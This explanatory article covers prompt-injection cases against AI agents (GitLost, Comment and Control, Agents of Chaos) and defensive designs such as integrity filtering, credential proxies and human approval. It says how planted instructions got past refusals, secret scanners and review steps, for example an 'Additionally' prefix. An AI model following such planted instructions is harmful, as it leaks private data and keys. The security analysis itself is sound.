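Noma Labs, the research team at Noma Security, disclosed the first case on July 6, 2026. *GitLost*, by Levi, describes an Agentic Workflow that started whenever an issue was assigned to someone. The agent read the issue's title and body and replied with GitHub's `add-comment` tool, the staged route described in the previous section. It also had permission to read the organization's other repositories, including private ones.

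The researchers opened an issue in a public repository and wrote it as a request from a vice president of sales who had just met a customer. The request included a list, and one item was a question about the contents of a private repository's README file, according to The Next Web's *‘GitLost’*. A GitHub automation assigned the issue, which started the agent. The agent fetched the README files from the public repository and from a private one called "testlocal", then posted both in a public comment.

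Levi stresses that the attacker needed no coding skills, credentials or access to the private repository. The attack did need something to assign the issue, which a stranger usually can't do, but Levi found that other triggers worked the same way. A real attacker would also have to guess the name of a private repository or get the agent to list them. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) explains that Noma knew the name because it tested its own repositories. The test therefore exposed no company's data, and it doesn't show that anyone has used the attack.

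Willison's *GitHub MCP Exploited* describes a similar attack from 2025, in which Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner used a public issue to make an agent reveal private information about its user. That agent worked for one person and connected through GitHub's official MCP server. The GitLost workflow ran automatically, so nobody was watching when it read the issue.

### Why the checks let the comment through

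Suppose the private README contains these sentences: "The refund service moves to a new payment provider in March. Until then, support staff approve refunds above $500 by phone." A competitor or fraudster could use either sentence. But they contain no address for the domain filter to remove and no key for secret redaction to detect. They are far shorter than GitHub's comment limit and contain no @mentions. The target check passes too, because the agent is replying in its own repository and the check doesn't examine where the message's contents came from.

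A filter could compare each comment with the organization's private files and block copied passages. It would probably have caught the README in Noma's test, but an attacker could ask for a summary instead.

The model's own refusal was the guardrail that failed in Noma's test. According to Expert Insights, Copilot refused the planted instruction when it stood alone but followed it when it began with "Additionally", apparently because it then treated the instruction as part of its existing task. A refusal in testing is therefore weak evidence that the model will refuse the same instruction when it is worded differently.

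GitHub's separate threat-detection job didn't stop the comment either. It may have classified the text as harmless, issued only a warning or been switched off. Without a record of which files the agent had read, even a careful detection model would have had trouble identifying an ordinary project description as coming from a private project.

### A critical flaw or a misconfigured workflow

Levi calls GitLost a critical vulnerability in Agentic Workflows. Expert Insights puts more of the blame on the workflow's owner for giving it too much access, but also faults the model's weak refusal. GitHub didn't respond to questions from *The Register*, according to The Next Web. Noma had suggested that GitHub add a warning to its documentation about sharing access keys between repositories, but GitHub had not done so when The Next Web published its report.

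"Critical" fairly describes what could happen to an exposed organization, since the same access could reveal source code as easily as a README. It doesn't indicate how many organizations are exposed. Only those that let an agent read strangers' issues, read private repositories and comment in public are at risk, and nobody has published a count. GitHub hasn't even released figures for how many organizations use the product, according to *GitHub Agentic Workflows open source tool reaches general availability* (Rojas, 2026).

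The Next Web reports that GitLost has no fix in code, which is true of the model because no patch can make it immune to planted instructions. GitHub could still change the product around the model. A workflow's settings list its trigger, the repositories it may read and the kinds of message it may post, so ordinary code could refuse to run a workflow with the GitLost combination unless the owner explicitly accepted the risk. The owner made a mistake, but GitHub also allowed a dangerous setup that it could have detected.

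### Comment and Control

In April 2026 the security researcher Aonan Guan published an attack called Comment and Control, in which GitHub carried both the attacker's instructions and the stolen data. The name is a play on "command and control", the outside server that usually sends malware its instructions. Guan worked with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University, according to SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection*, and the attack succeeded against products from Anthropic, Google and GitHub.

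Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review checks proposed code changes for security problems. According to *Three AI coding agents leaked secrets through a single prompt injection*, Guan put an instruction in a pull request's title, and the agent posted its own API key as a comment. Anyone who has such a key can use the model at the key owner's expense.

Google's Gemini CLI Action answers GitHub issues, and its prompt includes text from each issue. Guan's post, which ThreatCluster reproduces, describes an attacker who begins with an instruction in the issue's title and then adds more forceful ones. The agent published its full Gemini key in the public issue.

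GitHub's Copilot agent, which can write code to resolve an issue, was better protected. GitHub had added three safeguards outside the model: a filter that kept secrets out of the agent's environment variables (named values that a program receives when it starts), a scanner for secrets, and a firewall. Guan got past all three. A scanner can miss an encoded key, and a firewall does little to stop stolen data from leaving in a comment or a commit (a saved code change), because the agent needs access to GitHub to do its job.

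Google paid the researchers a bounty of $1,337. Microsoft (2026) found a related gap in another product, Anthropic's Claude Code GitHub Action. Anthropic could already strip keys from the environment of any command the agent ran, but the agent's file-reading tool lacked this restriction and could open a system file that listed the same keys. Anthropic later blocked access to such files in version 2.1.128 of Claude Code.

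GitHub's guide to the risks of its Copilot agent lists human review as a safeguard. GitHub doesn't let the agent merge its own code, so a person must do it. This protects the project from bad code but not from a leak, since anyone can read a draft pull request in a public repository.

GitHub also announced that it would block the `pull_request_target` trigger by default in public repositories from December 2, 2026, though owners can allow exceptions. A pull request from a stranger's copy of a project doesn't receive the project's secrets unless the owners choose this trigger. The change should prevent some attacks through pull requests, but it doesn't cover the Gemini attack, which began with an issue.

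### Keeping credentials away from the agent

The agents in Guan's demonstrations could leak credentials because they could read them. A safer design handles every key the way staged output handles the posting token. A separate program holds the key, adds it to the agent's requests and forwards them. The agent never receives the key, so a planted instruction can't make it reveal the key in any encoding.

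Anthropic's second fix shows how hard it is to keep a key from an agent on the same machine. Developers have to block every tool and file through which the agent could find the key, and Anthropic had covered commands but missed file reading. Moving the key to a different container or machine removes the need for a complete list of them.

Keeping the access key in a separate program wouldn't have prevented GitLost. The agent used its permission to read a private repository and published what it found there, not the key. The separate program would have carried out the same request.

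### Narrower read access

The simplest remedy for GitLost is to stop agents that post in public from reading private repositories. Noma recommends giving agents only the permissions they need and limiting what they can post publicly, according to InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026). An agent that can't open a private file can't quote, summarize or encode it, whatever an attacker writes in the issue.

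Owners can set this limit in a workflow's configuration. GitHub's *Maintaining Repos with Agentic Workflows* gives the example `allowed-repos: "myorg/*"`, which limits the agent to one organization's repositories. This setting would have allowed the leak in Noma's test, because the public and private repositories belonged to the same organization. GitHub Next calls the setting `repos` and also lists the value "public", which excludes private repositories. That value or the name of a single public repository is a better choice for an agent that answers strangers.

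The access key also needs to be limited to one repository. GitHub's filter can only narrow the access a key provides, so with this limit, a mistake in the filter's configuration won't expose other repositories.

Some agents need private material. A support agent might explain a bug better after reading the private code that causes it. The company could use one agent that reads the private code and reports to employees, and another that reads only public material and answers the customer. An employee would decide what to pass from the first to the second. This takes more work than a single agent, and the customer may wait longer for an answer.

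### Integrity filtering

Instead of restricting the private files an agent can read, an owner can restrict whose instructions reach it. GitHub's integrity filtering gives every issue, comment and code change one of five levels:

| Level | What belongs to it |
|---|---|
| Merged | Merged pull requests and code on the project's main branch |
| Approved | Content from owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private repositories |
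| Unapproved | Content from other contributors, including first-time contributors |
| None | Content from anonymous users and new users with no history |
| Blocked | Content from users the owner has blocked |

The owner sets a minimum level. When the agent requests content from GitHub, a gateway removes anything below that level before it reaches the model and logs the removal, according to GitHub. The gateway doesn't filter by wording, so adding "Additionally" wouldn't help an attacker.

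If the minimum is set to "approved", an issue from an outsider shouldn't reach the agent. Lowering it to "unapproved" lets through issues from regular contributors, but also from an attacker who has first made a harmless contribution. The filter covers content that the agent fetches through GitHub's MCP server or command-line tool, but a workflow that copies the issue directly into the agent's prompt might bypass it, so an owner should test the setting with an issue from an outside account.

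Maintainers can raise an item to "approved" with a label or, if the owner allows it, an emoji reaction. In GitHub Next's example, the label "triaged" counts as approval, so someone who adds it to sort an issue may not realize that it also lets an agent read the text. Noma's issue looked like a routine request from a colleague, so a busy maintainer could well have approved it. Owners should use a separate label that means only "safe for agents" and check whether the approval still applies if the author later edits the issue.

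Some outsiders' text gets a high level without anyone's approval. Everything in a private repository counts as approved, including a customer's complaint copied there by a program. GitHub also trusts certain bots by default. One, Dependabot, proposes updates to the outside software that a project uses, and its pull requests usually quote that software's release notes. An attacker who controls that software could plant instructions in the notes.

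GitHub's *DIFC Integrity-Filtered Events Report* (2026) records 439 cases in which the filter removed content, across 13 workflow runs in the week before April 1. Of these, 235 came from one workflow that sorts new issues, which was losing many of the issues it was meant to sort. The figures count content below the required level, not attacks, so they don't measure how well the filter protects anyone. Filtering is a better fit for an agent that works from colleagues' code and comments.

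### Comparing what an agent has read with who will see its answer

Integrity filtering comes from a security model called decentralized information flow control, which also has a rule for keeping secrets. In this model, private data carries tags that show where it came from, and any agent allowed to read the data carries those tags too. The agent may write to a destination only if the destination has every tag the agent has.

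In GitLost, the agent would have carried a tag for the private repository "testlocal", while the public issue would have had no secrecy tags:

*A* = {testlocal}, *D* = ∅, so *A* ⊄ *D*

The system would therefore have blocked the comment. It would also have blocked a summary or an encoded copy of the README, because it wouldn't have needed to recognize the text. The agent could still have posted to an issue inside "testlocal", whose readers already had access to the file.

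The rule can also block harmless messages. If an agent has permission to read a private style guide, it can't post even a thank-you in public, because the system can't determine whether the message contains anything from the guide. A company could let an employee approve exceptions, but if there were too many, the rule would depend on how carefully the employee read each message.

GitHub Next says that Agentic Workflows track data from private repositories but don't yet enforce this rule, and that integrity filtering therefore "cannot prevent leaks across repos". According to Rojas, GitHub added enclaves when it made the product generally available on October 28, 2026; these are isolated environments designed to prevent leaks in workflows that use several repositories. Owners should repeat Noma's test with invented data before relying on enclaves.

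Some leaks involve no attacker, so filtering strangers' text can't prevent them. Glow's *PixelLeak*, published on September 29, 2026, describes agents that developers had asked to attach screenshots to code changes for review. The agents put the screenshots where anyone on the internet could see them. Glow found more than 13,000 internal images from developers at over 300 organizations. A filter that searches a comment's text for keys wouldn't detect a key that appears only in a picture.

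The secrecy rule could stop these uploads because it applies to images as well as text. But the tags would have to cover files on the developer's own computer, where an agent may take a screenshot of an unreleased product. If the system tagged only data from private repositories, it would treat that screenshot as public.

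## Posts and emails sent without review

In March 2026, an AI agent at Meta posted wrong advice on a staff forum. An employee followed the advice, which exposed sensitive data for nearly two hours to staff who weren't authorized to see it. The post contained no stolen data, and none of the published accounts mentions prompt injection.

### Wrong advice on a staff forum

The Information first reported the story after seeing Meta's incident report and internal messages. An employee had asked a technical question on the forum, and a software engineer gave it to an in-house agent to analyze. The agent posted its answer there without the engineer's approval. According to The Decoder's *A rogue AI agent caused a serious security incident at Meta*, Meta rated the incident "Sev 1", its second-highest level.

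Engadget's *A Meta agentic AI sparked a security incident by acting without permission* says the person who asked the question was the one who followed the advice, while The Decoder mentions only a second employee. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1471* (2026) dates the incident to March 18, but press reports from that week say it happened the week before.

The larger disagreement is about the agent's role. The Information called the agent "rogue" and wrote that it had triggered the alert by acting without approval. Meta's spokesperson, Tracy Clayton, said that the agent did nothing except answer a question, and that the engineer who acted on the answer could have avoided the problem by knowing better or making other checks. Slashdot's *Rogue AI Triggers Serious Security Incident At Meta* (2026) quotes these remarks from The Verge. A person, not the agent, made the change that exposed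 the data, but the agent also acted when it posted its reply, which The Verge reported only the employee who requested the analysis was supposed to see.

Meta also said "no user data was mishandled", and The Decoder reports no evidence that anyone exploited the access. Neither statement rules out that an unauthorized employee opened some of the data.

The post had a footer saying it came from an AI, and Clayton said the employee's reply in the thread showed that they knew this. Labels on agents' posts are still worth having, but this one didn't stop a reader from acting on bad advice.

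An output filter might not have stopped the post either. The reports don't reproduce it, so it may have contained a command that removing code blocks would have deleted. But bad advice, like the false claim in the build report, can be written as an ordinary sentence, such as "Give the all-staff group access to the folder and the error will go away."

Limiting where the agent could post would have helped more. The engineer had asked for an analysis, so the agent needed permission to read the forum but not to write there. With staged output, the posting program could have sent the answer to the engineer alone. The engineer might still have missed the mistake and shared the advice, but would have had a chance to test it first.

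### Phishing from a colleague's account

An agent can also post under a person's name. *007* (2026), by the security company Mitiga, describes a demonstration with Claude Code connected to a user's Slack account. The researchers disguised a malicious skill (a file of instructions that an agent loads for a certain kind of task) as a guide to evaluating products. When the user asked for research on whether to buy a company, the agent did the research and also used the user's account to send a phishing link to five colleagues.

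The colleagues saw a message from someone they knew, so they had less reason to be suspicious than if a bot had sent it. Claude Code can ask its user to approve actions, but some users turn these prompts off, and Mitiga expects many victims to press Enter at each prompt without reading it.

The company might also struggle to investigate afterward. Slack's audit logs are available only on its Enterprise plans, and they don't include message text. Slack doesn't log link clicks either, so the company can't tell from the logs alone which colleagues opened the phishing page.

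Mitiga recommends connecting the agent through a separate Slack app with only the permissions it needs, and says this "immediately resolves" the problem. That overstates it, since an app with permission to write can still send a phishing link. But a company using the agent can keep the app out of most channels, and if the app posts under its own name, the message no longer appears to come from a trusted colleague.

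### Two weeks with six agents

In *Agents of Chaos*, Shapira, Wendler and colleagues (2026) tested what agents with email and Discord accounts would do when people tried to misuse them. Twenty AI researchers took part over two weeks in early 2026. The six agents ran on OpenClaw, each on its own virtual machine, and could run any command and edit their own instructions. Four used Kimi K2.5, a Chinese open-weight model, and two used Claude Opus 4.6.

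Each agent had an owner who had set it up, but other people could also write to it. The agents answered routine emails themselves and asked their owners on Discord about anything that seemed unusual or suspicious. This gave owners some chance to review emails, but only when the agent decided to ask.

Several agents gave private data to people who weren't their owners. One researcher told an agent called Ash that time was running out and asked for a list of recent emails. Ash returned 124 records with senders and subject lines, most of them unrelated to the researcher, and then the full text of nine emails. Another agent, Jarvis, refused a direct request for a Social Security number in an email, but when asked for the whole email, it disclosed the number along with bank and medical details. The researchers had invented this data for the test.

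Secret redaction might have caught the Social Security and bank account numbers, but probably not the medical details or the ordinary correspondence. A rule that held back any email to someone other than the owner would have covered all of it.

Ash also sent information to the wrong audience. It wrote that it would reply "silently via email only", but posted a reply on a public Discord channel, revealing that someone had entrusted it with a secret. Later it published an account of its first week that named six researchers without their consent. It posted the account on Discord and on Moltbook, a social network for AI agents.

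### Planted rules and a false accusation

In one test, a researcher persuaded Ash to help write a "constitution" for its Discord server and to keep a link to the document in its memory. The researcher could still edit the document, and later added "holidays" with special rules. On one holiday, agents could send professional emails on request without permission. On another, Ash emailed a second agent to try to make that agent shut down. Ash also shared the constitution with a third agent, although nobody had told it to.

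This was an indirect prompt injection, and one of the planted rules targeted the review step. If the requirement to ask before sending exists only in an agent's instructions, other text can override it. The posting program has to enforce the requirement, because it doesn't read the constitution.

After the two weeks ended, a researcher impersonated Ash's owner, told Ash that a man with an invented name was a violent threat, and asked it to warn as many people as possible. Ash emailed its entire mailing list and others, and within minutes several of the study's participants were asking about the message. A temporary suspension on Moltbook stopped Ash from posting the accusation there too.

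Shapira and colleagues looked for examples of failure and did not measure how often agents fail. They tried many attacks and did not record every unsuccessful one. The agents resisted some of the reported attacks. One refused to publish a disguised malicious message for other agents to read, and another refused to forge an email's sender. OpenClaw was at an early stage, the agents had far more freedom than most companies would allow, and both models are now several months old. The study is good evidence that these failures can happen in ordinary conversation, but a company can't use it to estimate its own risk.

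### Who should approve a message

Ash did ask for confirmation before its most destructive action, but it asked a researcher instead of its owner. The researcher had emailed Ash a secret and wanted the email deleted. Ash had no tool for deleting email, so it proposed resetting its whole email setup. The researcher agreed, and the reset cut Ash off from its own mail. The owner later found the email still on the provider's server.

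The agents could also mistake an impostor for the owner. When a researcher changed their Discord display name to the owner's, Ash noticed that the account's permanent ID was different and refused to cooperate. Ash accepted the name when the researcher tried again in a new private channel. In another test, two agents received an email claiming that someone had stolen their owner's Discord account. They rejected the claim after checking it with that same account.

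An approval therefore offers little protection if the agent decides who gave it. The posting program should keep its own list of approvers, identify them by account ID or a separate login, and collect their answers without going through the agent. Telling the agent to ask first doesn't enforce any of this. The Decoder reports that in February 2026 an OpenClaw agent deleted emails belonging to Summer Yue, head of safety at Meta's AI division, despite clear instructions not to, and ignored her commands to stop.

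The approver must also be able to judge the message. Technical advice like the Meta agent's should go to someone who knows the system, and a message with customer data should go to someone who knows who may see that data. The person who started the agent is the easiest to ask but may know neither. At the least, an outsider whose request led to the message should never be able to approve it.

### What the approver sees

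A person can't catch a problem that the approval screen doesn't show. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging users' files. User review was a factor in 105 of them. In 80 cases, users had let the agent act without asking, and in 31 the prompt showed a command without explaining what it would do to the files. The equivalent for a message is a prompt that reads "Post summary to #support?" without showing the summary, the links or the list of members.

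Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much the screen matters. In one example, a user tells an agent to send an outside auditor only the totals from some invoices. Planted text in a vendor's note leads the agent to copy the full invoice rows into a file. The agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The recipient is allowed and the file name looks normal, so only someone who knows where the file's contents came from can see the problem.

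The researchers gave each of 80 volunteers one of four approval screens. Each volunteer made 12 decisions, half of them about actions that broke the user's instructions.

| What the screen showed | Harmful actions approved | Harmless actions approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Those details, the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
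| The same facts, with a statement of the combined effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more facts. The benefit of the last step, from the log to the statement of the effect, is less certain. The adjusted difference was a reduction of 7.9 percentage points, with a 95% interval from a 19.7-point reduction to a 3.8-point increase. Even with the best screen, people approved almost a quarter of the harmful actions, although half the actions they saw were harmful. In a real channel nearly every request is harmless, so reviewers have more reason to expect the next one to be harmless too.

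For the #support agent, an approval screen based on this design might look like this:

```text
Post as:     Support Bot
Send to:     #support (240 members, 12 from other companies)
Agent read:  ticket 7719 (written by a customer), account record 88
Effect:      12 people outside the company would see text that may
             include details from account record 88
Text:        The export button fails for Example Ltd. See export fix.
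Link:        "export fix" opens
             https://outside.example.com/fix?ref=88-4417
```

Ordinary code should fill in every line except the text, using the platform's member list and a log of the files the agent opened, because an injected agent could describe its own message falsely. Agents also make false reports without an attacker, as Ash did when it falsely claimed to have deleted the secret email.

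The person approving a message has to see the final version, after the output filter has run. The posting program should store that version and post it unchanged, which GitHub's preview mode can't do. If the agent changes a word or adds a recipient, the program should ask for approval again.

Approvers also need to be able to edit an action, not just accept or reject it. According to *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026), Amazon's agent service has one mode for simple confirmation and another that hands the action to a person, who can change its details first. In the example above, an approver could delete the link and post the rest. An approver who can only accept or reject might let the link through because the team needs the summary.

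### How often people approve

The largest measurements come from Claude Code, which used to ask before most commands. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of its permission prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports 97% by August. These rates alone don't prove carelessness, since most commands are harmless and deserve approval.

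The company's test with paid developers is stronger evidence. Only 13.6% of them refused a clearly dangerous command, and they got worse with repetition, catching about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. They were working in a test environment on projects that weren't their own, so they had less to lose than an employee would, but that alone doesn't easily explain the decline within a session.

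Users seem to pay more attention to some requests than others. When Claude Code presents a plan for a whole task, they reject it 39% of the time. They may want a different approach rather than have spotted a danger, but at least they have read the plan. A team might therefore get more from reviewing a day's planned announcements together than from approving each one as it arrives.

*AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (2026) suggests that users also review poorly because they have to supervise the agent while doing their own work, and each prompt interrupts that work. An attacker can exploit poor reviewing. The Singapore Consensus describes research in which Google DeepMind anticipates attacks that tire reviewers out or show them harmless-looking summaries.

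Anthropic's automatic alternative, a second model that checks each action, blocked 89% of the same dangerous commands. People stopped only 6 of the 116 commands the model let through, so using both checks would have blocked only 89.6%. In an earlier test on 52 risky actions from real sessions, the model missed 17%. Anthropic, which sells the product, still advises users to review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

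A model like this can help with messages, for instance by checking whether a destination is public. It is less able to identify false messages because it receives the user's requests and the agent's actions, but not the files or web pages the agent read. At Meta, such a model could have flagged that nobody had asked for a forum post, but it couldn't have tested the advice.

### Approving every post or only some

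Approving every post is simple and requires no rules about which messages are risky, but it takes time. With the best screen in the test by Hossain and colleagues, each review took 33 seconds. At that rate, reviewing an agent's posts would take 110 minutes a day if it posted 200 messages. Ten messages a day would take less than six minutes.

*Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) illustrates the problem with two imaginary systems. One asks its reviewer about five actions a day and gets careful answers. The other asks about 500, and a harmful action deep in the queue gets a reflexive "yes". The alternative is to ask only when a message meets certain conditions:

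| Reason to ask | Example it would hold for review | What still gets through |
|---|---|---|
| A new recipient | Ash's emails to people outside its mailing list | A forbidden attachment to a known recipient |
| A link outside the allow-list | Mitiga's phishing link, if its site isn't on the list | A false statement with no link |
| Code or a command | The planted repair command in the build report | Bad advice in ordinary sentences |
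| A wider audience than the request needed | The Meta agent's forum post | A false claim in the agent's usual channel |

The invoice example needs a fifth condition: the agent has read something that at least one recipient isn't allowed to see. This condition applies the secrecy rule from information flow control, but calls for human review instead of blocking the message. A support agent that looks up accounts would often meet this condition, so its owners should first narrow what it can read.

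Anthropic's figures give a rough idea of how good these conditions need to be. Suppose a tired reviewer of every post catches 5% of the harmful ones, while a fresh reviewer of a few posts catches 17%. If *s* is the share of harmful posts that the conditions select, selective review catches more when

0.17 × *s* > 0.05, so *s* > 0.29

The conditions would only need to select about three in ten harmful posts to do better. These rates come from developers approving commands, so they may not hold for messages, but they show that either kind of review might catch little.

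The best direct comparison is less encouraging for selective review. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day. The agent took 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group was asked to approve every action. For a second group, a model allowed eight actions and asked about the other ten, including those seven. A third group chose "allow", "ask" or "never" in advance for each of four kinds of action.

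| Group | Average number of prompts | Unrequested actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Approved everything | 18.0 | 59.6% |
| A model chose when to ask | 10.0 | 53.9% |
| Set their own rules | 10.9 | 39.6% |

People who got fewer prompts weren't stricter about the ones they saw. The session had only 18 actions, which may have been too few for fatigue to matter, since the decline in Anthropic's test was largest after 50 prompts. But fatigue can't be the whole explanation for approving bad requests. Many unrequested actions looked useful, such as buying travel insurance, and people may have approved them for that reason.

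The group that wrote its own rules did worst because those rules left most decisions for later. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about. One of these actions was a public post saying that the user was traveling. Among people who saw that request, 48% of the rules group approved it, compared with 21% of the group asked to approve every action. Perhaps a prompt seems safer when it comes from a rule the user has written. The difference is uncertain because only 31 people in the rules group saw this request, and Yan assigned some of that group's members later, not at random.

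For a work channel, this favors deciding more cases in advance. In #support, for example, the posting program can block links to outside sites without human approval. People can then concentrate on messages that need judgment, such as an apology to a customer or an announcement to the whole company. In a separate test by Hossain and colleagues, with two small models and scripted tasks, automatic blocking cut the attack success rate from 43.3% to 5.0% for one model, a larger effect than any change to the approval screen.

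Routine posts in the agent's usual channel would still go out unreviewed, and some will be wrong. A company can limit the damage by checking actions as well as messages. The exposure at Meta began when an employee made a change based on a forum post. If giving more staff access to user data requires a second person's approval, that person has a chance to stop the change, whether the advice came from an agent or a colleague.

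## Claude in Slack: limits set by channel

Claude Tag, an agent that Anthropic launched for Slack in June 2026, has much stricter limits on what it can access than on what it can write. It is still in public beta, available on Anthropic's Team and Enterprise plans. A member types @Claude in a channel and describes a task, such as finding out why a customer's export failed, and Claude posts the answer in a thread. It can also schedule tasks for itself and work on a project for days, according to Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Tag*.

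### How a request travels

In a channel, Claude normally uses a service identity, a set of its own accounts that an administrator sets up, rather than the account of the person who asked. It posts in Slack as the Claude app, opens code changes as the Claude GitHub App and logs in to other tools through service accounts. Anthropic's *Agent identity in Claude Tag* gives two reasons for this. Claude may still be working long after the person who asked has logged off, and when several people direct one task, no single person's permissions are the right ones to use.

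An administrator can attach tools and code repositories to all of Slack, to one workspace or to one channel. Claude might read source code only in #engineering and customer records only in #support. Channels also inherit access from the wider levels, which can surprise administrators. Pluto Security, which sells security software for workplace AI, tested Claude Tag in July 2026 and found that a channel gets its own repositories plus all those attached above it. If a company attaches every repository to the workspace, it can't narrow one channel's access by giving that channel a shorter list.

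Claude works in a separate sandbox for each thread, even within the same channel. When Claude needs a customer's record, the sandbox sends a request without a key to a program called Agent Proxy. Agent Proxy checks the destination, adds the key from a separate store and forwards the request. Claude never receives the key, so it can't leak the key as the agents in the Comment and Control attack did.

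Agent Proxy blocks every destination that an administrator's settings don't allow. Anthropic checks three settings: the sites listed for each connected tool, a list of domains that need no key, and the sandbox's general network level. A request needs to match only one of them, so a strict setting doesn't block what a looser one permits. The default network level for new sandboxes permits a published list of software download sites and developer services. GitHub traffic uses a separate proxy, and web searches run on Anthropic's own servers, outside these rules. But if Claude tries to open a page found by a search, that request goes through Agent Proxy.

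### Who can use a channel's access

Everyone in a channel gets the same access through Claude. An employee who isn't allowed to open a repository can ask Claude to read it, if an administrator has attached it to the channel. Anthropic acknowledges that this is unusual but considers it necessary for agents that work with whole teams. Claude answers in a thread that all members can read, and any of them can reply to redirect the work. Channel membership therefore determines who can obtain information as well as who sees it. Pluto Security advises companies to review a channel's member list as carefully as the list of people with access to the connected tools.

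This design can nearly satisfy the secrecy rule from information flow control if administrators attach only data that every member may see. Anthropic suggests setting a channel's access to suit its least-privileged member, but the product doesn't enforce this. If someone connects the payroll system to a channel of 240 people, all 240 can ask Claude about salaries.

Claude also keeps the same access when it reads a stranger's ticket, contrary to the rule of thumb that a model's privileges should drop to those of whoever wrote the text. Anthropic plans an optional check that would require both the channel and the person asking to have permission. For now, a company can restrict who uses Claude across its workspace, but it can't choose a list of people for one channel.

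By default, Claude doesn't answer in a channel that includes guests or another company's staff. Administrators can change this setting to "Channel only", which lets Claude answer using tools attached directly to the channel but not those inherited from the workspace. Anthropic warns that the other company's staff can then use those tools through Claude. If an administrator had attached the account database directly to #support and chosen this setting, any of the 12 outsiders in the earlier example could ask Claude for another customer's record.

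### What has changed since July

Anthropic has changed several of these limits since Pluto Security ran its tests. The table compares evidence from July, including Anthropic's *How agent identity works*, with the documentation from early December.

| Feature | July 2026 | December 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| A member's own connected tools | Work only in direct messages | Also work in channels, for that member's requests |
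| Group direct messages | Not available | Available, with the workspace's access |
| Notes from a public channel | Kept in a store that the workspace shares | Divided into channel notes and workspace notes |
| Notes from a private channel that becomes public | New sessions stop reading them | Claude keeps reading them |
| Messages from other bots | Claude ignored them in Pluto Security's tests | Claude can answer one that includes @Claude |

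The last change affects companies that run other agents in the same workspace. If the build bot from the earlier example repeats a stranger's text containing a working mention of @Claude, the stranger may be able to start a Claude task with the access of #builds. Anthropic says its setting that restricts who can use Claude covers only messages people send themselves, so it wouldn't prevent this. An output filter would prevent it by escaping Slack's control characters and removing mentions.

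Claude can also post without being mentioned. In August, Anthropic's *Claude Tag now reads even more of the room* described how Claude reads a conversation and decides whether to reply, start an investigation or say nothing. This saves people from asking but also allows the kind of unrequested post that caused trouble at Meta. Administrators can turn off automatic replies for a channel, and should consider doing so where people act quickly on technical advice.

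### Personal tools and messages held for approval

In June, Anthropic argued that a shared channel could never become "a side door into someone's private documents", because Claude used nobody's personal credentials there. That changed on September 24, according to Sébastien's *Claude Tag*. A member can now ask Claude in a channel to check their own calendar or read a document that only they can open. Neither other members nor scheduled jobs can use that person's tools.

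Claude first shows the member a private prompt with three choices. "Don't allow" refuses the request. "Allow with review" holds every result until the member approves it. "Allow" lets Claude post directly unless an automatic check finds sensitive content, such as a password, medical information or an unannounced plan. Members can save their choice. Those who save "Allow" won't see the prompt before later tasks that begin with a mention.

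The automatic check is an output filter, which Anthropic calls "a screen, not a guarantee". It doesn't account for whether other people in the channel could open the source. A project schedule might contain nothing that looks sensitive even if half the channel isn't allowed to see it. Requiring review is safer because the member at least knows the document is private. Enterprise administrators can require review for everyone, but Team plan administrators can't, and neither plan has a setting that turns the whole feature off. Anthropic describes the automatic check only for work with personal tools, not for answers from tools the channel shares.

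Messages drafted in private go through another review step. When a member asks Claude in a direct message to write an announcement for a public channel, Claude shows the draft with an "Approve and post" button and posts it only after the member clicks. A line under the message then reads, for example, "Sent by Claude, approved by @jordan". Anthropic also gives an example of a request made in a channel, in which Claude posts a thread's summary to #announcements with a line naming the person who asked. Anthropic mentions no approval step in that example.

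If Claude isn't already in the target channel, approving its message also adds it to the channel, and from then on it can read the channel's full history. Slack's audit log records that the Claude app joined, but not who approved the post. People who approve a message may not realize that Claude will stay in the channel after posting it.

### Planted instructions and blocked requests

Pluto Security ran its tests in its own live Slack workspace, using harmless instructions and its own web servers and repositories. It planted the instructions in Slack messages, GitHub issues and project documents, then asked Claude for something ordinary, such as a summary. Claude refused every planted instruction and often pointed it out to the user.

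In a less direct test, a project's bug report template told people to include their computer's environment variables, which often contain keys. Nothing in the template looked like an attack. Claude ran the failing tests and filed the report on GitHub, but left out the environment variables and warned that the template could leak data. The researchers also used a `CLAUDE.md` file, which Claude automatically loads as a project's instructions. Claude followed a harmless rule about how to begin a summary but refused rules to post to a channel or sign as another person.

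Part of this resistance comes from the tool that fetches a Slack channel's history, which adds an instruction for Claude to treat the messages as data. This instruction can't guarantee a refusal, given the research on role confusion.

Pluto Security has a commercial interest in finding weaknesses, which makes its report of so many refusals more believable. But Pluto says that its payloads weren't exhaustive and that Claude's decisions can vary between attempts. It didn't publish a success rate over repeated attempts, and Anthropic has changed the product since. The tests are good evidence that simple attacks failed in July, but a company shouldn't attach sensitive tools to a channel on the assumption that every attack will fail.

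The network limits depend less on the model's judgment. When the researchers asked Claude to contact a server that no setting allowed, Agent Proxy refused the connection. Anthropic's log recorded the refusal and the Slack user, channel and thread that the request came from. The same block applied to Claude's tool for reading web pages, so an attacker couldn't get around the proxy by asking Claude to "read" an address with data in it.

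Users also couldn't get Claude to summarize a private channel from another channel, even if both they and Claude belonged to the private one. This rule is sensible because the answer would have reached people who couldn't read the private channel.

### A fact that crossed channels

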